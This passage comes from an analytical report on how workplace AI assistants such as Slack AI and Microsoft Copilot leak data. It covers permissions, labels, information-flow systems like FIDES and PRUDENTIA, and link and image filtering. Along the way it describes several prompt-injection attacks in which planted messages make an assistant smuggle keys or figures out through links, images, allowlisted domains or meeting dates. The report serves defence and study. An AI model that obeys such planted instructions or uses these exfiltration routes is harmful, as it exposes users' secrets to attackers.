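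Stricter permissions would not have helped, because the victim was already the only member of the private channel that held the key. Restricting access further would have locked them out of their own notes.

### The compiler that overwrote the bills

Programmers have known a version of this problem for decades. Norm Hardy's *The Confused Deputy*, published in 1988, tells a "nearly true story" from Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers:

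1. Customers could run a compiler, a program that translates code, and name a file for its debugging output.
2. The compiler also kept usage statistics in its home directory, SYSX, so Tymshare gave it permission to write files there.
3. Tymshare kept its billing records in the same directory, in a file called BILL.
4. A customer learned that name and gave it to the compiler as the place for the debugging output.
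5. The compiler had permission to write in SYSX, so the operating system let it write over the billing records.

The compiler had authority from both the customer who ran it and the company that installed it, and it had no way to indicate which authority it was using. Hardy considered making the compiler reject certain file names, but BILL was not the only sensitive file in SYSX, and some people had good reasons to write there. He preferred to use a "capability", a token that identifies a file and grants the right to use it. A customer with no right to change BILL would have had no such token to give the compiler.

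Like the compiler, a workplace assistant can use the victim's authority to carry out the attacker's request. *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (2026) lists three differences. The hostile request arrives inside a document, email or tool response instead of as a direct command. The model's decision depends on wording and chance. The authority is spread over a chain of people, programs and services.

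In its example, a user asks an agent to summarise the invoices in an inbox, and one of the messages requests a payment. The agent passes the request to a second agent that handles finance, without passing on the restriction that the task was read-only. The payment service receives a valid credential and makes the payment. It can verify which program is calling, but it can't detect that a stranger's email prompted the call.

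Capabilities could prevent that payment, because an agent that only summarises invoices would have no payment token to pass on. They would protect a password already in the context less well, since an ordinary model can copy any text it has been given into any part of its answer.

*A Framework for Formalizing LLM Agent Security* (2026) defines a confused deputy more narrowly, as an agent that opens something its signed-in user is not allowed to open. By that definition, Slack AI was not a confused deputy, because the victim was allowed to read the key. It was one only if we count the attacker as the person making the request, which seems closer to what happened. A company that tests only for the narrow version would therefore have found nothing wrong with Slack AI.

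### What "LLM scope violation" adds

Aim Labs describes the flaw in EchoLeak as occurring after retrieval, when an outsider's text directs the model to internal data without the user's explicit consent. Ravia compares this to a "suid" program on Unix, which runs with its owner's rights, so someone with few rights can misuse it to reach protected files.

The definition suggests that an instruction written by person a should affect only items in R(a). The permission check lacks this rule, which would have stopped both the Slack AI leak and EchoLeak.

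A rule that limited the assistant to files that the person who wrote each instruction can open would be hard to enforce, because the model writes its answer from the whole context and keeps no reliable record of which instruction produced which word. The rule would also block ordinary work. If a customer emails to ask when an order will ship, the employee wants the assistant to look up the answer in files that the customer can't open.

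In *Breaking down 'EchoLeak', the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability*, a commentary on Aim Labs' article of the same name, Willison (2025) doubts that scope violations are new or need their own term. Willison argues that prompt injection has always stemmed from models' inability to take account of where text came from. Ravia argues that precise categories help people build precise defences, as the term "stack overflow" did for one kind of memory error. Aim Labs also had a reason to want a separate category, because it had a product to offer against scope violations.

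Willison is right that the mechanism is old. The term is still useful because prompt injection also includes attacks that don't steal private data, such as the fake login link in Slack AI.

### Does removing one part of the lethal trifecta suffice?

*The lethal trifecta for AI agents* (Willison, 2025) provides a simple test for identifying at-risk assistants before an attack, which Hardy's story and Aim Labs' term do not. An attacker can steal data from an assistant that can access private data, is exposed to untrusted content and can communicate externally.

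The test applies to a combination of tools. Each tool may be harmless alone, and its maker cannot see which other tools an employee has combined it with. A single tool can also have all three properties. GitHub's MCP server, for example, could read public reports filed by strangers, open private code and publish changes.

In principle, removing any one of the three would stop an outsider from stealing stored secrets. In practice, each is difficult to remove completely.

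An assistant that can't read the company's messages can't leak passwords stored in them, but it also can't do its job. An attacker could still use it to show employees a phishing link, as PromptArmor did without needing any secret.

Excluding strangers' email from what the assistant could read would have stopped EchoLeak, but not the attack on Slack AI, where the planted message came from an account inside the workspace, or SearchLeak, where the instructions were in a link to Copilot's own search page.

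According to Willison, vendors have usually fixed such leaks by blocking the route the data took. Microsoft did this several times, but researchers then got data out through a saved document and a code sandbox.

A leak doesn't need a web address. *Enterprise AI Must Enforce Participant-Aware Access Control* (Bhatt, Rajore and colleagues, 2025), a paper from Microsoft, describes an attacker called Bob who emails Alice to suggest a meeting. Hidden text in the email tells her assistant to look up a project's revenue in millions and propose that number as the date. When Alice asks for a draft reply, the assistant finds the figure of $7 million and suggests 7 May. Alice sees nothing odd in the draft and sends it.

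This route leaks very little data, and Bob has to know what to ask for. But the data leaves in the reply that Alice wanted to send, so a filter on links and images would not catch it.

### Whose rights does the assistant use?

The trifecta describes theft by an attacker. A colleague can also learn something they shouldn't when nobody is attacking, depending on whose rights the assistant uses. Suppose a company has three documents, and these people and a bot can open them:

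| Document | Priya, human resources | Tom, manager | Lena, engineer | Bot |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Launch plan | Yes | Yes | Yes | Yes |
| Note about job cuts in February | Yes | Yes | No | No |
| Salary list | Yes | No | No | Yes |

**When the assistant has the asker's rights,** it can use only the launch plan to answer Lena but all three documents to answer Priya, so Lena can't get the salary list through it. An attacker who plants a message can steal only what the person asking can read, and so gains more if Priya's question retrieves the message than if Lena's does.

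The bot can use its own rights to open the salary list, perhaps because an administrator connected it to the personnel system to answer questions about holidays. If Lena asks for everyone's salary and the bot answers, she learns something outside R(Lena), even though nobody planted any text. This is the narrow kind of confused deputy, which *A Framework for Formalizing LLM Agent Security* illustrates with a similar salary request.

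The developer could prevent this by checking Lena's rights as well as the bot's, but those rights may be hard to determine. *DEPUTYBENCH* (2026), a test of company agents, notes that they can depend on approvals, consent or the current version of a policy. Business systems record these things, but Lena's request doesn't mention them.

In Agent 365, Microsoft's service for running AI agents among a company's staff, an agent can act for a user, as an application with its own permissions, or as a kind of employee with its own account and email address. In its guide to the preview version, Microsoft warns that an agent may reveal content one person shared with it to people who don't have access to that content, regardless of its labels or permissions. Microsoft advises users to treat agents as "public collaborators".

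**In a shared channel,** the asker's rights are no longer enough. Priya asks the assistant, in front of Tom and Lena, what could delay the launch. The assistant searches with Priya's rights, finds the note and replies that the job cuts in February might. Lena has now learned about the job cuts. The note was in R(Priya), so the usual check passed, and no data left the company. The assistant needed a stricter check:

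C ⊆ R(Priya) ∩ R(Tom) ∩ R(Lena)

The symbol ∩ keeps only what all three people may read, which here is the launch plan.

Bhatt and colleagues propose applying this rule to everyone involved in a conversation, including the recipients of an email. It would stop Bob's attack, because Bob cannot read the revenue figure. However, the assistant can use less information as more people join, and almost none if one of them is a client. Bhatt and colleagues would let Alice approve an exception for drafts that a person reviews. *Authorization Before Context* (2026) applies a similar rule to an assistant's stored memories, and defines the audience by the channel's members rather than its name. This may still miss someone who joins the channel later and reads the old messages.

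Some products already have a version of this check. Slack returns only public results when someone calls an outside assistant in a public channel. According to Microsoft's *Share an agent from SharePoint in Teams*, SharePoint agents use the asker's permissions in a Teams chat. If other members lack access to the answer, the asker has to preview it and decide whether to post it. The agents don't answer if guests are present. In the example, the preview would let Priya stop the reply if she noticed what it revealed.

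Leaving the decision to the model is much less reliable. Ruzzetti, Emde and colleagues (2026), in *MuPPET*, generated 562 group conversations among coworkers, in which an assistant spoke for one employee and knew something private about them, such as a health condition. Each conversation ended with an ordinary work question. The researchers told the model which people should not receive the information, and compared its answers to the group with its answers to one such person alone:

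| Model | Leaked to one person | Leaked to the group |
|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.5 | 14% | 27% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 10% | 23% |

Without such a warning, the models leaked the private fact to the group in 49% and 39% of conversations. A strict privacy instruction cut both rates to about 9% but made the answers less useful. Real rates could differ because the conversations were synthetic and another language model judged the leaks. Newer models may also do better. Still, a permission check would have excluded a forbidden item every time if the permissions were right.

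### When R(u) is larger than anyone intended

Access permissions often let people open more than anyone meant them to, for example because someone shared a folder with the whole company years ago and forgot about it. Microsoft's *Assess and Remediate Data Oversharing for Copilot Readiness* calls this oversharing the largest data security risk in deploying Copilot. Copilot doesn't give anyone new access, but an employee who would never have browsed to a forgotten personnel folder can now find it by asking a question.

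Redmond (2026), in *Microsoft Copilot Implementation To Dos in Late 2026*, recalls that before Copilot, permissions were "an unmanaged jungle" and companies relied on obscurity for security. In John (2026), *A viral TikTok about Copilot leaking layoffs is a joke*, Michael Bargury of Zenity, which sells monitoring for AI agents, says that companies counted on the effort of searching to discourage curious employees, but an agent doesn't get tired. He also says Zenity has seen "many cases" of agents revealing information to the wrong employees, but gives no number.

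Oversharing also makes planted messages more dangerous. The attacker can steal only what the victim can read, and every forgotten folder adds to that.

Two surveys from September 2026 suggest that the problem is common. *Over 75% of Organizations Experience Microsoft 365 Governance Issues* (Muncaster, 2026) reports that 29% of the nearly 1,800 IT professionals and leaders in ShareGate's survey said an AI tool had surfaced sensitive internal data it should not have had access to. Yet 93% were sure their controls were ready for AI.

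*Most Organizations Skip Permissions Reviews Before Deploying AI Tools* (Poireault, 2026) reports a Syskit survey of 327 people responsible for Microsoft 365 at larger British and American organisations. Only 43% had fully reviewed permissions before deploying AI tools, and 41% left SharePoint sites open to all staff. In addition, 9% let an agent inherit the full permissions of whoever deployed it, which could give a junior colleague an administrator's access.

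Scans of files do not rely on what respondents know or admit. Concentric AI's *Data Risk Report* (2025) examined customers' data from January to June 2025 and found that, on average, 57% of the records shared with a whole organisation contained sensitive information. This figure does not show what proportion of their sensitive records companies shared. Concentric AI left out values below 1,000, assuming that those customers had already fixed the problem, so its average counts are probably too high for a typical company.

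Varonis found sensitive files open to all employees through Copilot at 90% of the organisations it studied, according to CPABC's *Proactive Steps Needed to Mitigate AI’s Impact on Data Security*. Cyera's *Announcing the Copilot Risk Report* puts the typical number of such files at more than 23,000.

ShareGate, Syskit, Concentric AI, Varonis and Cyera all sell tools for finding or fixing these problems, and the file counts depend on what each company calls sensitive. None of the figures measures how many employees read something they shouldn't have. Microsoft sells such tools too, but it also sells Copilot, so its own warning about oversharing is more credible than another vendor's percentage. *Microsoft Copilot Deployments Delayed Over Security Concerns* (Palmer, 2026) reports that two-thirds of organisations in a CoreView survey had delayed or cancelled Copilot for fear of exposing confidential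 data.

### What does "only what users can already view" cover?

Microsoft usually replies that Copilot shows users only what they already have permission to view. In 2024, Slack similarly called searching public channels "intended behavior".

The reply is mostly fair as a statement about C ⊆ R(u). Lena can't use Copilot to open a private channel she doesn't belong to, which is an important protection. But this protection applies only when the assistant uses the asker's access rights, and it limits only what the asker sees. It doesn't stop a server from receiving a link with a password in it, or colleagues from reading the answer in a shared channel. It also doesn't help if the permissions were set incorrectly.

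Microsoft gave this reply again in February 2026, after a bug made Copilot Chat return content from emails labeled confidential in users' own Drafts and Sent Items folders. Their companies had set policies meant to stop Copilot from using those emails. Microsoft told ITPro that the bug did not give anyone "access to information they weren’t already authorized to see" (*Microsoft Copilot bug saw AI snoop on confidential emails*).

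The users could already read the emails because they had written them, but the policies were meant to control what Copilot processed. Once a confidential email is in Copilot's context, an attacker can use a planted message to try to make Copilot copy the email into a link, even if only the person who wrote it asked for it.

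## How far does limiting the assistant's data reduce the risk?

A company can let its assistant read less than the employee who uses it can read. An attacker can steal a stored secret only if the secret and the planted message are in the same context, so keeping either one out prevents the theft. Most of the limits that Slack and Microsoft offer are better at keeping out secrets than at keeping out planted messages.

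### Searching fewer channels

In the 2024 attack on Slack AI, the planted message was in a public channel that the victim had never joined. An assistant that searched only the channels its user had joined would not have found it. The attacker would have had to post in one of those channels, where the victim's colleagues were more likely to notice the message.

The permission that every outside program needs to search Slack also covers public channels the user hasn't joined. Slack's narrowing of results by where the employee asks would have stopped the 2024 attack only in some places. Suppose the key is in a private channel and the planted message is in a public one:

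| Where the employee asks | What the search covers | Can it return the key? | Can it return the planted message? |
|---|---|---|---|
| A public channel | Public channels | No | Yes |
| The private channel with the key | That channel and public channels | Yes | Yes |
| A channel shared with another company | That channel only | No | No |
| An outside app with permission to search private channels | The user's private channels and public channels | Yes | Yes |

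The private channel is where an employee would most naturally ask about the key, and there the search can return both texts.

Developers could build a stricter search themselves, limited to channels the user has joined. Slack's MCP server can list those channels, and the search interface accepts channel names as filters. But employees would then get no answers from other teams' channels, and those answers may be much of the reason for having an assistant, especially for new staff. Slack gives no figures on how many useful answers come from channels the user hasn't joined.

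Companies on Slack's Enterprise+ plan can instead close particular channels to AI. According to Slack's *Restrict AI access to certain channels, canvases, and lists*, this applies to search answers, Slackbot's responses and the text that AI writes for canvases (Slack's shared documents). The setting suits a channel where engineers exchange passwords during outages. It would do little against a planted message, because an administrator can't restrict an attacker's new channel before learning that it exists.

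The setting also limits only what the AI reads. Members can still use Slackbot to post in a restricted channel, so a misleading answer based on other channels could end up there.

### Leaving out files, guests' posts and outside email

In 2025, Slack let administrators exclude either all files from the assistant's answers or only linked ones, such as documents in Google Drive. The second option still allowed files uploaded to Slack, so it would not have blocked the PDF with hidden instructions that PromptArmor had warned about, which would count as internal once an employee uploaded it. Slack's *Privacy Principles* also lists emails among the uploaded files that the assistant can use, so a stranger's email could reach it the same way.

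Excluding all files from the assistant's data prevents attacks that use files, but the assistant can then no longer answer employees' questions from reports, contracts and presentations. In 2024, PromptArmor sensibly recommended restricting the assistant's access to files until Slack had resolved the problem. However, this would not have stopped either of the attacks PromptArmor had demonstrated, because both used only messages.

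Administrators can also stop Slackbot from searching the web, another source of text written by strangers. They need to review their settings from time to time, because Slack automatically adds new functions wherever Slackbot is on, and only some have a separate switch.

Guests' messages are harder to exclude. Slack doesn't let guests use apps with its AI features, but a full member's assistant may retrieve messages that guests write. Searches can also return messages from channels shared with other companies. None of the Slack controls described here filters messages by author, so to leave out guests' posts, a company would have to restrict every channel in which guests can write. Those are often the channels where employees discuss work with clients and contractors, and where a summary would be useful.

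Excluding outside email from Copilot's searches would have prevented EchoLeak and all three ReLeak attacks, but it would also prevent Copilot from telling a salesperson what a customer had ordered. As a compromise, the assistant could read outside email only when the user selects a message. This would stop attacks that rely on Copilot retrieving an email nobody mentioned, but not Rehberger's 2024 attack, in which the victim asked about the attacker's email.

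### Fewer permissions for connected programs

Slack (2026) announced its MCP server and the current version of its search interface in February 2026, and divided a broad search permission into separate ones for public channels, private channels, direct messages, group direct messages and files. If an administrator grants only the permission for public channels, a search can't bring a key from a private channel into the assistant's context, but it can still bring in a key that somebody pasted into a public channel.

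Slack limits a program more tightly when it searches as a bot instead of as a user. A bot can't search private channels or direct messages, and each search must include a temporary token that the bot receives when someone mentions or messages it. A bot therefore can't search Slack unprompted, but an attacker who has planted a message could still exploit a search that an employee prompted.

Companies can limit what the assistant writes as well as what it reads. Sending a message through Slack's MCP server requires a separate permission, and a program without that permission can't post a link for Slack to preview. Employees then have to copy useful answers into Slack themselves. This prevents the automatic request that a preview makes, but the program can still show a dangerous link in its own window, where an employee might click it.

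When an outside program needs approval to join a workspace, Slack shows the administrator which permissions the program requests and which other MCP servers it connects to. The administrator can refuse individual servers. This review is probably the best time to notice that a program would both read private messages and write to an outside service.

Slack can also reject requests from unfamiliar network addresses. This helps if someone steals a program's token and uses it elsewhere, but it doesn't stop a planted message, which works through the genuine program at its expected address.

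### Slack's 2025 limits on bulk copying

In May 2025, Slack restricted how quickly some outside apps could read the history of a channel or thread. *Rate limit changes for non-Marketplace apps* (2025) sets the limit at one request per minute and 15 messages per request. The limit applies to commercial apps that Slack hasn't approved for its Marketplace, except where a customer had already installed them. A company's own internal apps can still make at least 50 requests per minute, with up to 1,000 messages per request.

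At the lower rate, an app would need more than two days to copy a channel with 50,000 messages, while an internal app could do it in about a minute. The limit makes it much harder for an unreviewed app to copy a whole workspace, which was Slack's stated reason for imposing it. It does little to prevent the leaks described here, because a single message can contain a password.

Slack's new terms prohibit bulk exports and permanent copies or indexes of data obtained through its programming interfaces, according to National Law Review's *Salesforce Locks Down Slack Data* (2025). These limits matter more for old secrets, because an outside assistant that keeps its own index, instead of searching Slack live, can still find a password after its owner has deleted it from Slack.

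The change inconvenienced the many customers who had relied on such copies to search Slack together with their other records, and it hampered companies that compete with Slack's own AI search. According to National Law Review, the terms forbid using the data in language models, but Slack's developer guide allows programs to give search results to a model as context and forbids training on them.

### Deleting old messages and replacing secrets

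A shorter retention period reduces the number of secrets an assistant can find. If employees post secrets at a steady rate, a company that keeps messages for 90 days instead of four years stores about 94% fewer of them. The risk falls by less than that, because the newest secrets are the most likely to still work. An attacker's planted messages also expire, but the attacker can post new ones.

With short retention periods, the company also loses the answers in its old conversations. An employee who asks why the company chose a supplier may need a thread from two years ago. Companies could set short periods only for the channels where people troubleshoot or share access details, though secrets also turn up elsewhere.

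Deleting a message doesn't disable the password in it, which may keep working for years. A company that finds a password in chat should change the password first and then delete the message. The old password is then useless to a thief, even if an assistant leaks it later. The other limits in this section don't help once a leak has succeeded.

A company can replace only the secrets that a scanner or a person has noticed, and it can't replace a salary or a sales forecast. One-time login codes expire before anyone could find and remove them, but an attack like SearchLeak can send one out within seconds of the victim's click.

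### Microsoft's labels and data-loss rules

Microsoft 365 lets companies attach a sensitivity label, such as "Confidential", to a file or email. If the label also encrypts the item, Copilot returns its contents only to users who have both the VIEW right, to read the item, and the EXTRACT right, to copy text from it. A company can therefore let employees read a document but keep it out of Copilot's answers by granting them VIEW without EXTRACT.

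Companies can also write a data loss prevention (DLP) rule that stops Copilot from processing anything with a chosen label. Copilot may still list the item among its sources, but it doesn't use the contents. Microsoft offers "restricted content discovery" to hide a whole SharePoint site from Copilot while still letting employees with access open its files.

All of these controls can keep a secret out of the assistant's context. They do much less to keep out planted messages, because a stranger's email normally arrives without any of the company's labels.

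The DLP rule also has gaps. Microsoft says the rule covers only emails sent since 1 January 2025 and doesn't cover calendar invitations. A change to a rule can take four hours to reach Copilot. The rule at first worked only for files in SharePoint and OneDrive, but Microsoft announced an extension to files stored elsewhere, including on the user's own computer, in a notice reposted in itelio's *DLP policies will be able to block Copilot processing of sensitivity‑labeled files*.

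The gap is larger for workplace chat. Microsoft says that Copilot doesn't recognise the labels that protect Teams meetings and chats. Channel messages don't inherit their team's label either. In Microsoft's example, messages from a team labelled Confidential appear in Copilot's summaries without that label. A company that relies on labels may therefore protect its contracts well but leave the passwords that employees paste into Teams unprotected.

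Another kind of DLP rule, which Microsoft describes as a preview, checks what the user types. If the prompt contains something like a credit card number, Copilot can refuse to answer or answer without searching the web. This prevents employees from disclosing such data by mistake. In the attacks on Slack AI and Copilot, however, the check would have found nothing in the prompts, because the victims typed ordinary questions and the secrets came from stored text.

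### The rule that missed two folders

The Copilot fault of early 2026 showed that a correctly written DLP rule can fail without the customer noticing. According to Office365ITPros' *Code Error Allowed Copilot Chat to Expose Confidential Information* (2026), customers first reported on 21 January that Copilot Chat was using emails their rules should have excluded. In an advisory on 3 February, Microsoft attributed the fault to a "code issue" that affected the Sent Items and Drafts folders. By 10 February, a fix was reaching customers.

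The emails in those folders were the users' own, but they could contain text written by other people. TechRadar's *Microsoft admits an Office bug exposed confidential user emails to Copilot* assumes that Copilot could read whole threads there, including incoming messages.

On 20 February, Microsoft said the repair had reached most affected systems. TechInformed reports that the public versions of the advisory did not include the number of organisations or emails involved, or the date the fault began. The fault may have existed for some time before anyone reported it.

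Microsoft's advisory listed the Office365ITPros writer's organisation as affected, but the writer had not noticed the problem until a reader left a comment. After the fix, the writer sent a confidential email about an invented "Project Bunny" and asked Copilot about it. Copilot replied that it had found a reference but could not disclose the contents.

Office365ITPros reasonably asks why Microsoft had not tried something similar with Sent Items, which holds every confidential email that someone has sent. Customers can run the same test themselves from time to time, with a labelled dummy secret in each folder, because testing only the inbox would have missed this fault.

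### Labels that follow text to its destination

A DLP rule either lets the assistant read an item or keeps it out. Information-flow labels let the assistant use the item but restrict where the result can go. Each item carries a list of its permitted readers, and text based on several items may go only to people who appear on every list:

readers of the answer = readers of item 1 ∩ readers of item 2 ∩ …

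Before sending an answer, the system checks that every recipient is allowed to read it. The previous section used the same intersection of permissions to decide what an assistant could retrieve for a group. Here the label listing permitted readers stays attached to the text, so the system can also check destinations that nobody anticipated when the search ran.

Suppose Ana has a note that only she may read, and her company has a public channel open to all 500 staff. When Ana asks the assistant a question, it can use the note, the channel, or both. The 12-person channel in the table contains only staff.

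| Source of the answer | Permitted readers | Private reply to Ana | Reply in a 12-person channel | Request to an outside server |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Public channel | 500 staff | Allowed | Allowed | Blocked |
| Ana's note | Ana | Allowed | Blocked | Blocked |
| Both | Ana | Allowed | Blocked | Blocked |

The last row shows the main drawback. Once the assistant has read Ana's note, it can't post the answer in the 12-person channel, even if every word came from the public source. The system can't reliably tell which source influenced which word, so it has to assume that the note influenced all of them. In a long conversation, one private item can limit where the assistant is able to post every later answer.

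The system must also treat a web address as a message to the server it points to. Otherwise, it would have allowed the Slack AI leak, because only the victim saw the answer.

The reader rule doesn't stop an attacker from misusing the assistant among permitted readers. A planted message could make the assistant post a false payment request in the 12-person channel, using only information that all 12 people may read. A separate rule addresses this by requiring text to be labelled as trusted or untrusted. Untrusted text may not determine where a message goes or trigger any other consequential action, and anything based partly on untrusted text is also untrusted.

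Ana's own request is trusted, so she can tell the assistant to send a colleague a summary of a stranger's email. The email can supply the words of the summary, but it can't change who receives the summary.

### How FIDES applies the rules

Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, describe FIDES, a research system from Microsoft that enforces both rules with ordinary program code. The model can propose a forbidden action, but the code won't carry it out. If Ana asks for a summary of her three latest emails and wants it sent to her colleague Ben, FIDES works like this:

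1. It fetches the emails and stores their text under a name, such as `emails-1`. The model that plans the work sees only the name.
2. The planning model asks a separate model, which has no tools, to summarise `emails-1`.
3. FIDES stores the summary as `summary-1`, with labels based on those of the emails.
4. The planning model requests that FIDES send `summary-1` to Ben, and FIDES checks the request against its rules.

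A planted instruction to send the emails to `attacker.example` can't affect step 4, because the planning model never reads it. The instruction could still spoil the summary, for example by making the separate model return an empty one.

Some tasks require information from an email. When Ana asks the assistant to add a meeting to her calendar only if somebody has requested one, the planning model's next step depends on whether there is a request. FIDES can limit the separate model's answer to yes or no, which leaves no room for an instruction. The planning model can also read the email directly, but FIDES then marks the whole context as untrusted and blocks most later actions.

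Costa and colleagues tested FIDES on AgentDojo, a public test suite that simulates office work, travel booking, banking and Slack. They used 97 ordinary tasks and 36 attacks, and paired each task with every attack from the same setting. The main tests used OpenAI's GPT-4o.

Without any rules, 152 attacks succeeded against an ordinary assistant, while none succeeded with the rules. FIDES without its rules still let 21 through because the planning model sometimes opened the planted text. These counts exclude cases the researchers considered harmless or wrongly scored, including three that AgentDojo had counted against the full version of FIDES.

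An ordinary assistant with the same rules also stopped every attack. The advantage of FIDES was that it could usually do more work under them. These are the shares of tasks completed when nobody was attacking:

| Simulated setting | Ordinary assistant, no rules | Ordinary assistant with rules | FIDES with rules |
|---|---|---|---|
| Office work | 75.0% | 37.0% | 59.0% |
| Travel | 70.0% | 73.0% | 41.0% |
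| Banking | 98.8% | 37.5% | 52.5% |
| Slack | 93.3% | 20.0% | 47.6% |

The Slack result is the most relevant here, and few companies would accept an assistant that failed at about half of such tasks. Some of the losses came from the model's mistakes. In one Slack task, it requested a list of channels it didn't need, which made the context untrusted. OpenAI's o1, which was better at reasoning, raised FIDES's travel score to 68%, and current models would probably do better.

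Other losses come from the rules themselves. Many of the banking tasks asked the assistant to read a file and follow its instructions, such as paying a bill. FIDES is designed to block this, since an attacker could have written the file. A better model can't avoid this loss unless a person decides the file is trustworthy.

The security result depends on correct labels, and the test made labelling easy. The researchers marked a type of field as untrusted if any AgentDojo attack used it, but a real company doesn't know in advance where attackers will write. Reader lists can also be wrong. FIDES's designers used an email's sender and recipients to infer who may read it, but someone may have shared it more widely since.

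The tested version also checked actions but not the answers shown to the user, which it treated as harmless. The Slack AI and EchoLeak leaks both went out through such answers, the first in a link and the second in an image. Costa and colleagues say that a developer can apply the rules to answers too, and a workplace assistant would need this.

By the summer of 2026, Microsoft had still not applied this research to its own product, at least for images. In one of the ReLeak attacks, the attacker could still violate the destination rule by using a planted email to specify the outside server to which Copilot's image request would send data.

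### A successor that asks for less approval

Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues, most of them at Microsoft, argue in *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (2026) that comparisons like the one above are unfair to FIDES. Many real assistants ask a person to approve each consequential action, but the test credited the ordinary assistant with tasks it completed without asking anyone. The researchers therefore counted how often each system would need approval.

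They also built PRUDENTIA, an extension of FIDES that tells the planning model about the labels and rules so that it can avoid breaking them. With OpenAI's o3-mini on AgentDojo, the systems completed these shares of tasks without any approval:

| System | Completed without approval |
|---|---|
| Ordinary assistant that asks before every consequential action | 24.3% |
| Ordinary assistant with information-flow rules | 35.5% |
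| FIDES | 50.1% |
| PRUDENTIA | 59.1% |

When people could approve actions that the rules would otherwise block, FIDES and PRUDENTIA completed similar numbers of tasks. With OpenAI's o4-mini, FIDES completed 75.7% of tasks with an average of 36.8 approvals over the whole test, while PRUDENTIA completed 73.2% with 19.2 approvals.

FIDES and PRUDENTIA followed the same rules in these tests, which were less strict about outgoing data than the reader rule alone. The rules allow a message if every recipient is a permitted reader or if the decision to send it came from a trusted context. Ana could therefore send her private note to a client on purpose, but a planted email could not make the assistant send it.

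In another test, on simulated versions of GitLab and Reddit, PRUDENTIA stopped all the attacks and needed no approvals. Attacks diverted an ordinary assistant in 14.6% to 61.1% of cases, depending on the model and site. The tasks were only to comment on or upvote a post, so PRUDENTIA never had to read the untrusted text. Finding the action items in a long email thread is harder because the assistant has to read the thread.

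For such tasks, PRUDENTIA can ask the user to endorse a piece of text, which marks it as trusted. If an email contains a list of ten jobs, one endorsement replaces ten separate approvals. In their measurements, Kolluri and colleagues assume that people approve harmless requests and stop attacks. They acknowledge that people who see frequent prompts may start approving them without thinking, and they leave the design of clearer prompts to later work.

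A careless endorsement could do more damage than a careless approval, which allows only one action. If the email with ten jobs also contains a planted instruction, a user who endorses the email makes that instruction trusted too, and PRUDENTIA will no longer stop the assistant from following it.

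## How should links, images and other outgoing requests be handled?

Commercial assistants, unlike FIDES and PRUDENTIA, tend to rely on rules that each cover only one kind of outgoing request, such as links or images.

Any request to an outside server can carry data, even if its address contains nothing secret. Microsoft (2025) lists images, clickable links, tool calls and "covert channels" as ways data can leak. As an example of a covert channel, if an attacker can observe whether the assistant used a certain tool, a planted message can leak one bit by making the assistant use the tool for "yes" and not use it for "no".

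Most of the measures below act after the model has written an answer or chosen a tool. Microsoft calls a measure deterministic if it guarantees that a particular attack fails, even when the model obeys the planted message. The guarantee covers only that attack, so a ban on images doesn't prevent leaks through links.

### Links that an employee might click

A program between the model and the screen can delete every outside link from an answer. This would have stopped the Slack AI leak, whatever the planted message said. But the program has to recognise every way of writing a link, which Copilot's filter failed to do in 2025. It also removes useful links, such as one to a supplier's price list.

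According to Google's *Mitigating prompt injection attacks with a layered defense strategy* (2025), Gemini checks links with Safe Browsing, Google's service for identifying dangerous sites, and replaces only the suspicious ones with "suspicious link removed". An attacker might get past this check by registering a new site with no bad record, and Google doesn't say whether Gemini also looks for private data in a link's address.

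Another option is to rewrite links. Google Colab, a service for writing and running code in a browser, puts a google.com address in front of each link. Clicking the link opens a Google page that asks for confirmation, and the attacker's server receives nothing unless the user continues. Embrace The Red found that links to Google's own sites skipped this page, so an attacker could still lure someone straight into a Google Meet call.

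A confirmation page is more useful if it shows the full address, because an employee might then spot `DUMMY-KEY` at the end. But a planted message can include an instruction to encode the key first. In base64, a common encoding, `DUMMY-KEY` becomes `RFVNTVktS0VZ`, which looks like the reference codes in many ordinary links. OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) says that ChatGPT's Safe Url safeguard shows the user the information that would be sent. But the warning in OpenAI's published example only displays the address, so a busy reader might still miss an encoded key.

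Removing invisible characters from an answer deletes any secret hidden in them before a link can send it to the attacker. The attacker can switch to visible characters, but then the employee has a chance of noticing them.

### Images and link previews

A browser requests an image without waiting for a click, so a warning beside the image would come too late. The safest rule is to load no images from outside addresses, and Google says Gemini does this.

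Any block on outgoing requests has to apply wherever someone might view the answer. PromptArmor's *OpenAI API Logs Unpatched Data Exfiltration* describes apps whose developers had blocked images. When a developer reviewed a flagged answer in OpenAI's log viewer, the viewer loaded an image in the answer and sent the data to the attacker.

Microsoft's Copilot Cowork had a similar gap in May 2026. Willison reports that the agent could email its own user without approval. The email could contain external images, which loaded when the user opened it. The image addresses could include OneDrive download links that needed no further login, so one short address could expose an entire file.

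Link previews are easier to control. In Slack, a developer can turn them off by setting `unfurl_links` and `unfurl_media` to `false` in each message a bot posts, according to Embrace The Red. A colleague can still click the link. If someone pastes it into their own message, Slack will fetch it by default, because the bot's settings apply only to the bot's message.

A company that installs a third-party bot depends on the bot's developer to add the settings. PromptArmor has proposed a channel-wide preview setting, which would let a company protect a channel even if a developer forgot to add them.

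### Why allowlists leak

An allowlist permits requests to the addresses on it and blocks all others. The content security policy that let Copilot load images from Microsoft's own sites is one example. Companies can also give an assistant's tools a list of permitted sites.

A list can work exactly as designed and still let data out, as in these cases that Willison collected:

| Product | Permitted destination | How the data could leave |
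|---|---|---|
| Superhuman's email assistant | The domain of Google Docs | An image address submitted the data to the attacker's Google Form |
| Claude Cowork | Anthropic's programming interface | The agent uploaded files with the attacker's API key, so the attacker could retrieve them |
| Salesforce Agentforce | A domain whose registration had expired | Researchers registered the domain and read its server's log |
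| Google Antigravity | A public site for recording web requests | The attacker created a page there and read its log |

Superhuman and Claude Cowork allowed requests to well-known companies' domains, but anyone can create a Google Form or open an Anthropic account. Approving a domain therefore lets the assistant send data to anyone who can receive it there.

An allowlist doesn't prevent leaks through a relay, which is a permitted site that fetches any address it receives. The allowlist permits the assistant's request to the relay, which then passes the key to the attacker, as Teams and Bing did in the attacks on Copilot.

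Redirects look similar to relays, because a permitted page can forward the visitor to another site. A program can check each new address before following a redirect, but it can't check the address a relay contacts, because that second request starts on someone else's server.

trackr.live's *The Model Writes the URL That Leaks Your Data*, a blog post, sensibly advises companies to consider the host, the path and the owner of each permitted destination. Permitting only a folder of company logos is much safer than permitting the whole site that stores them. Somebody also has to check the list regularly. After the Agentforce leak, Salesforce corrected its list and stopped the agent from writing links to untrusted domains.

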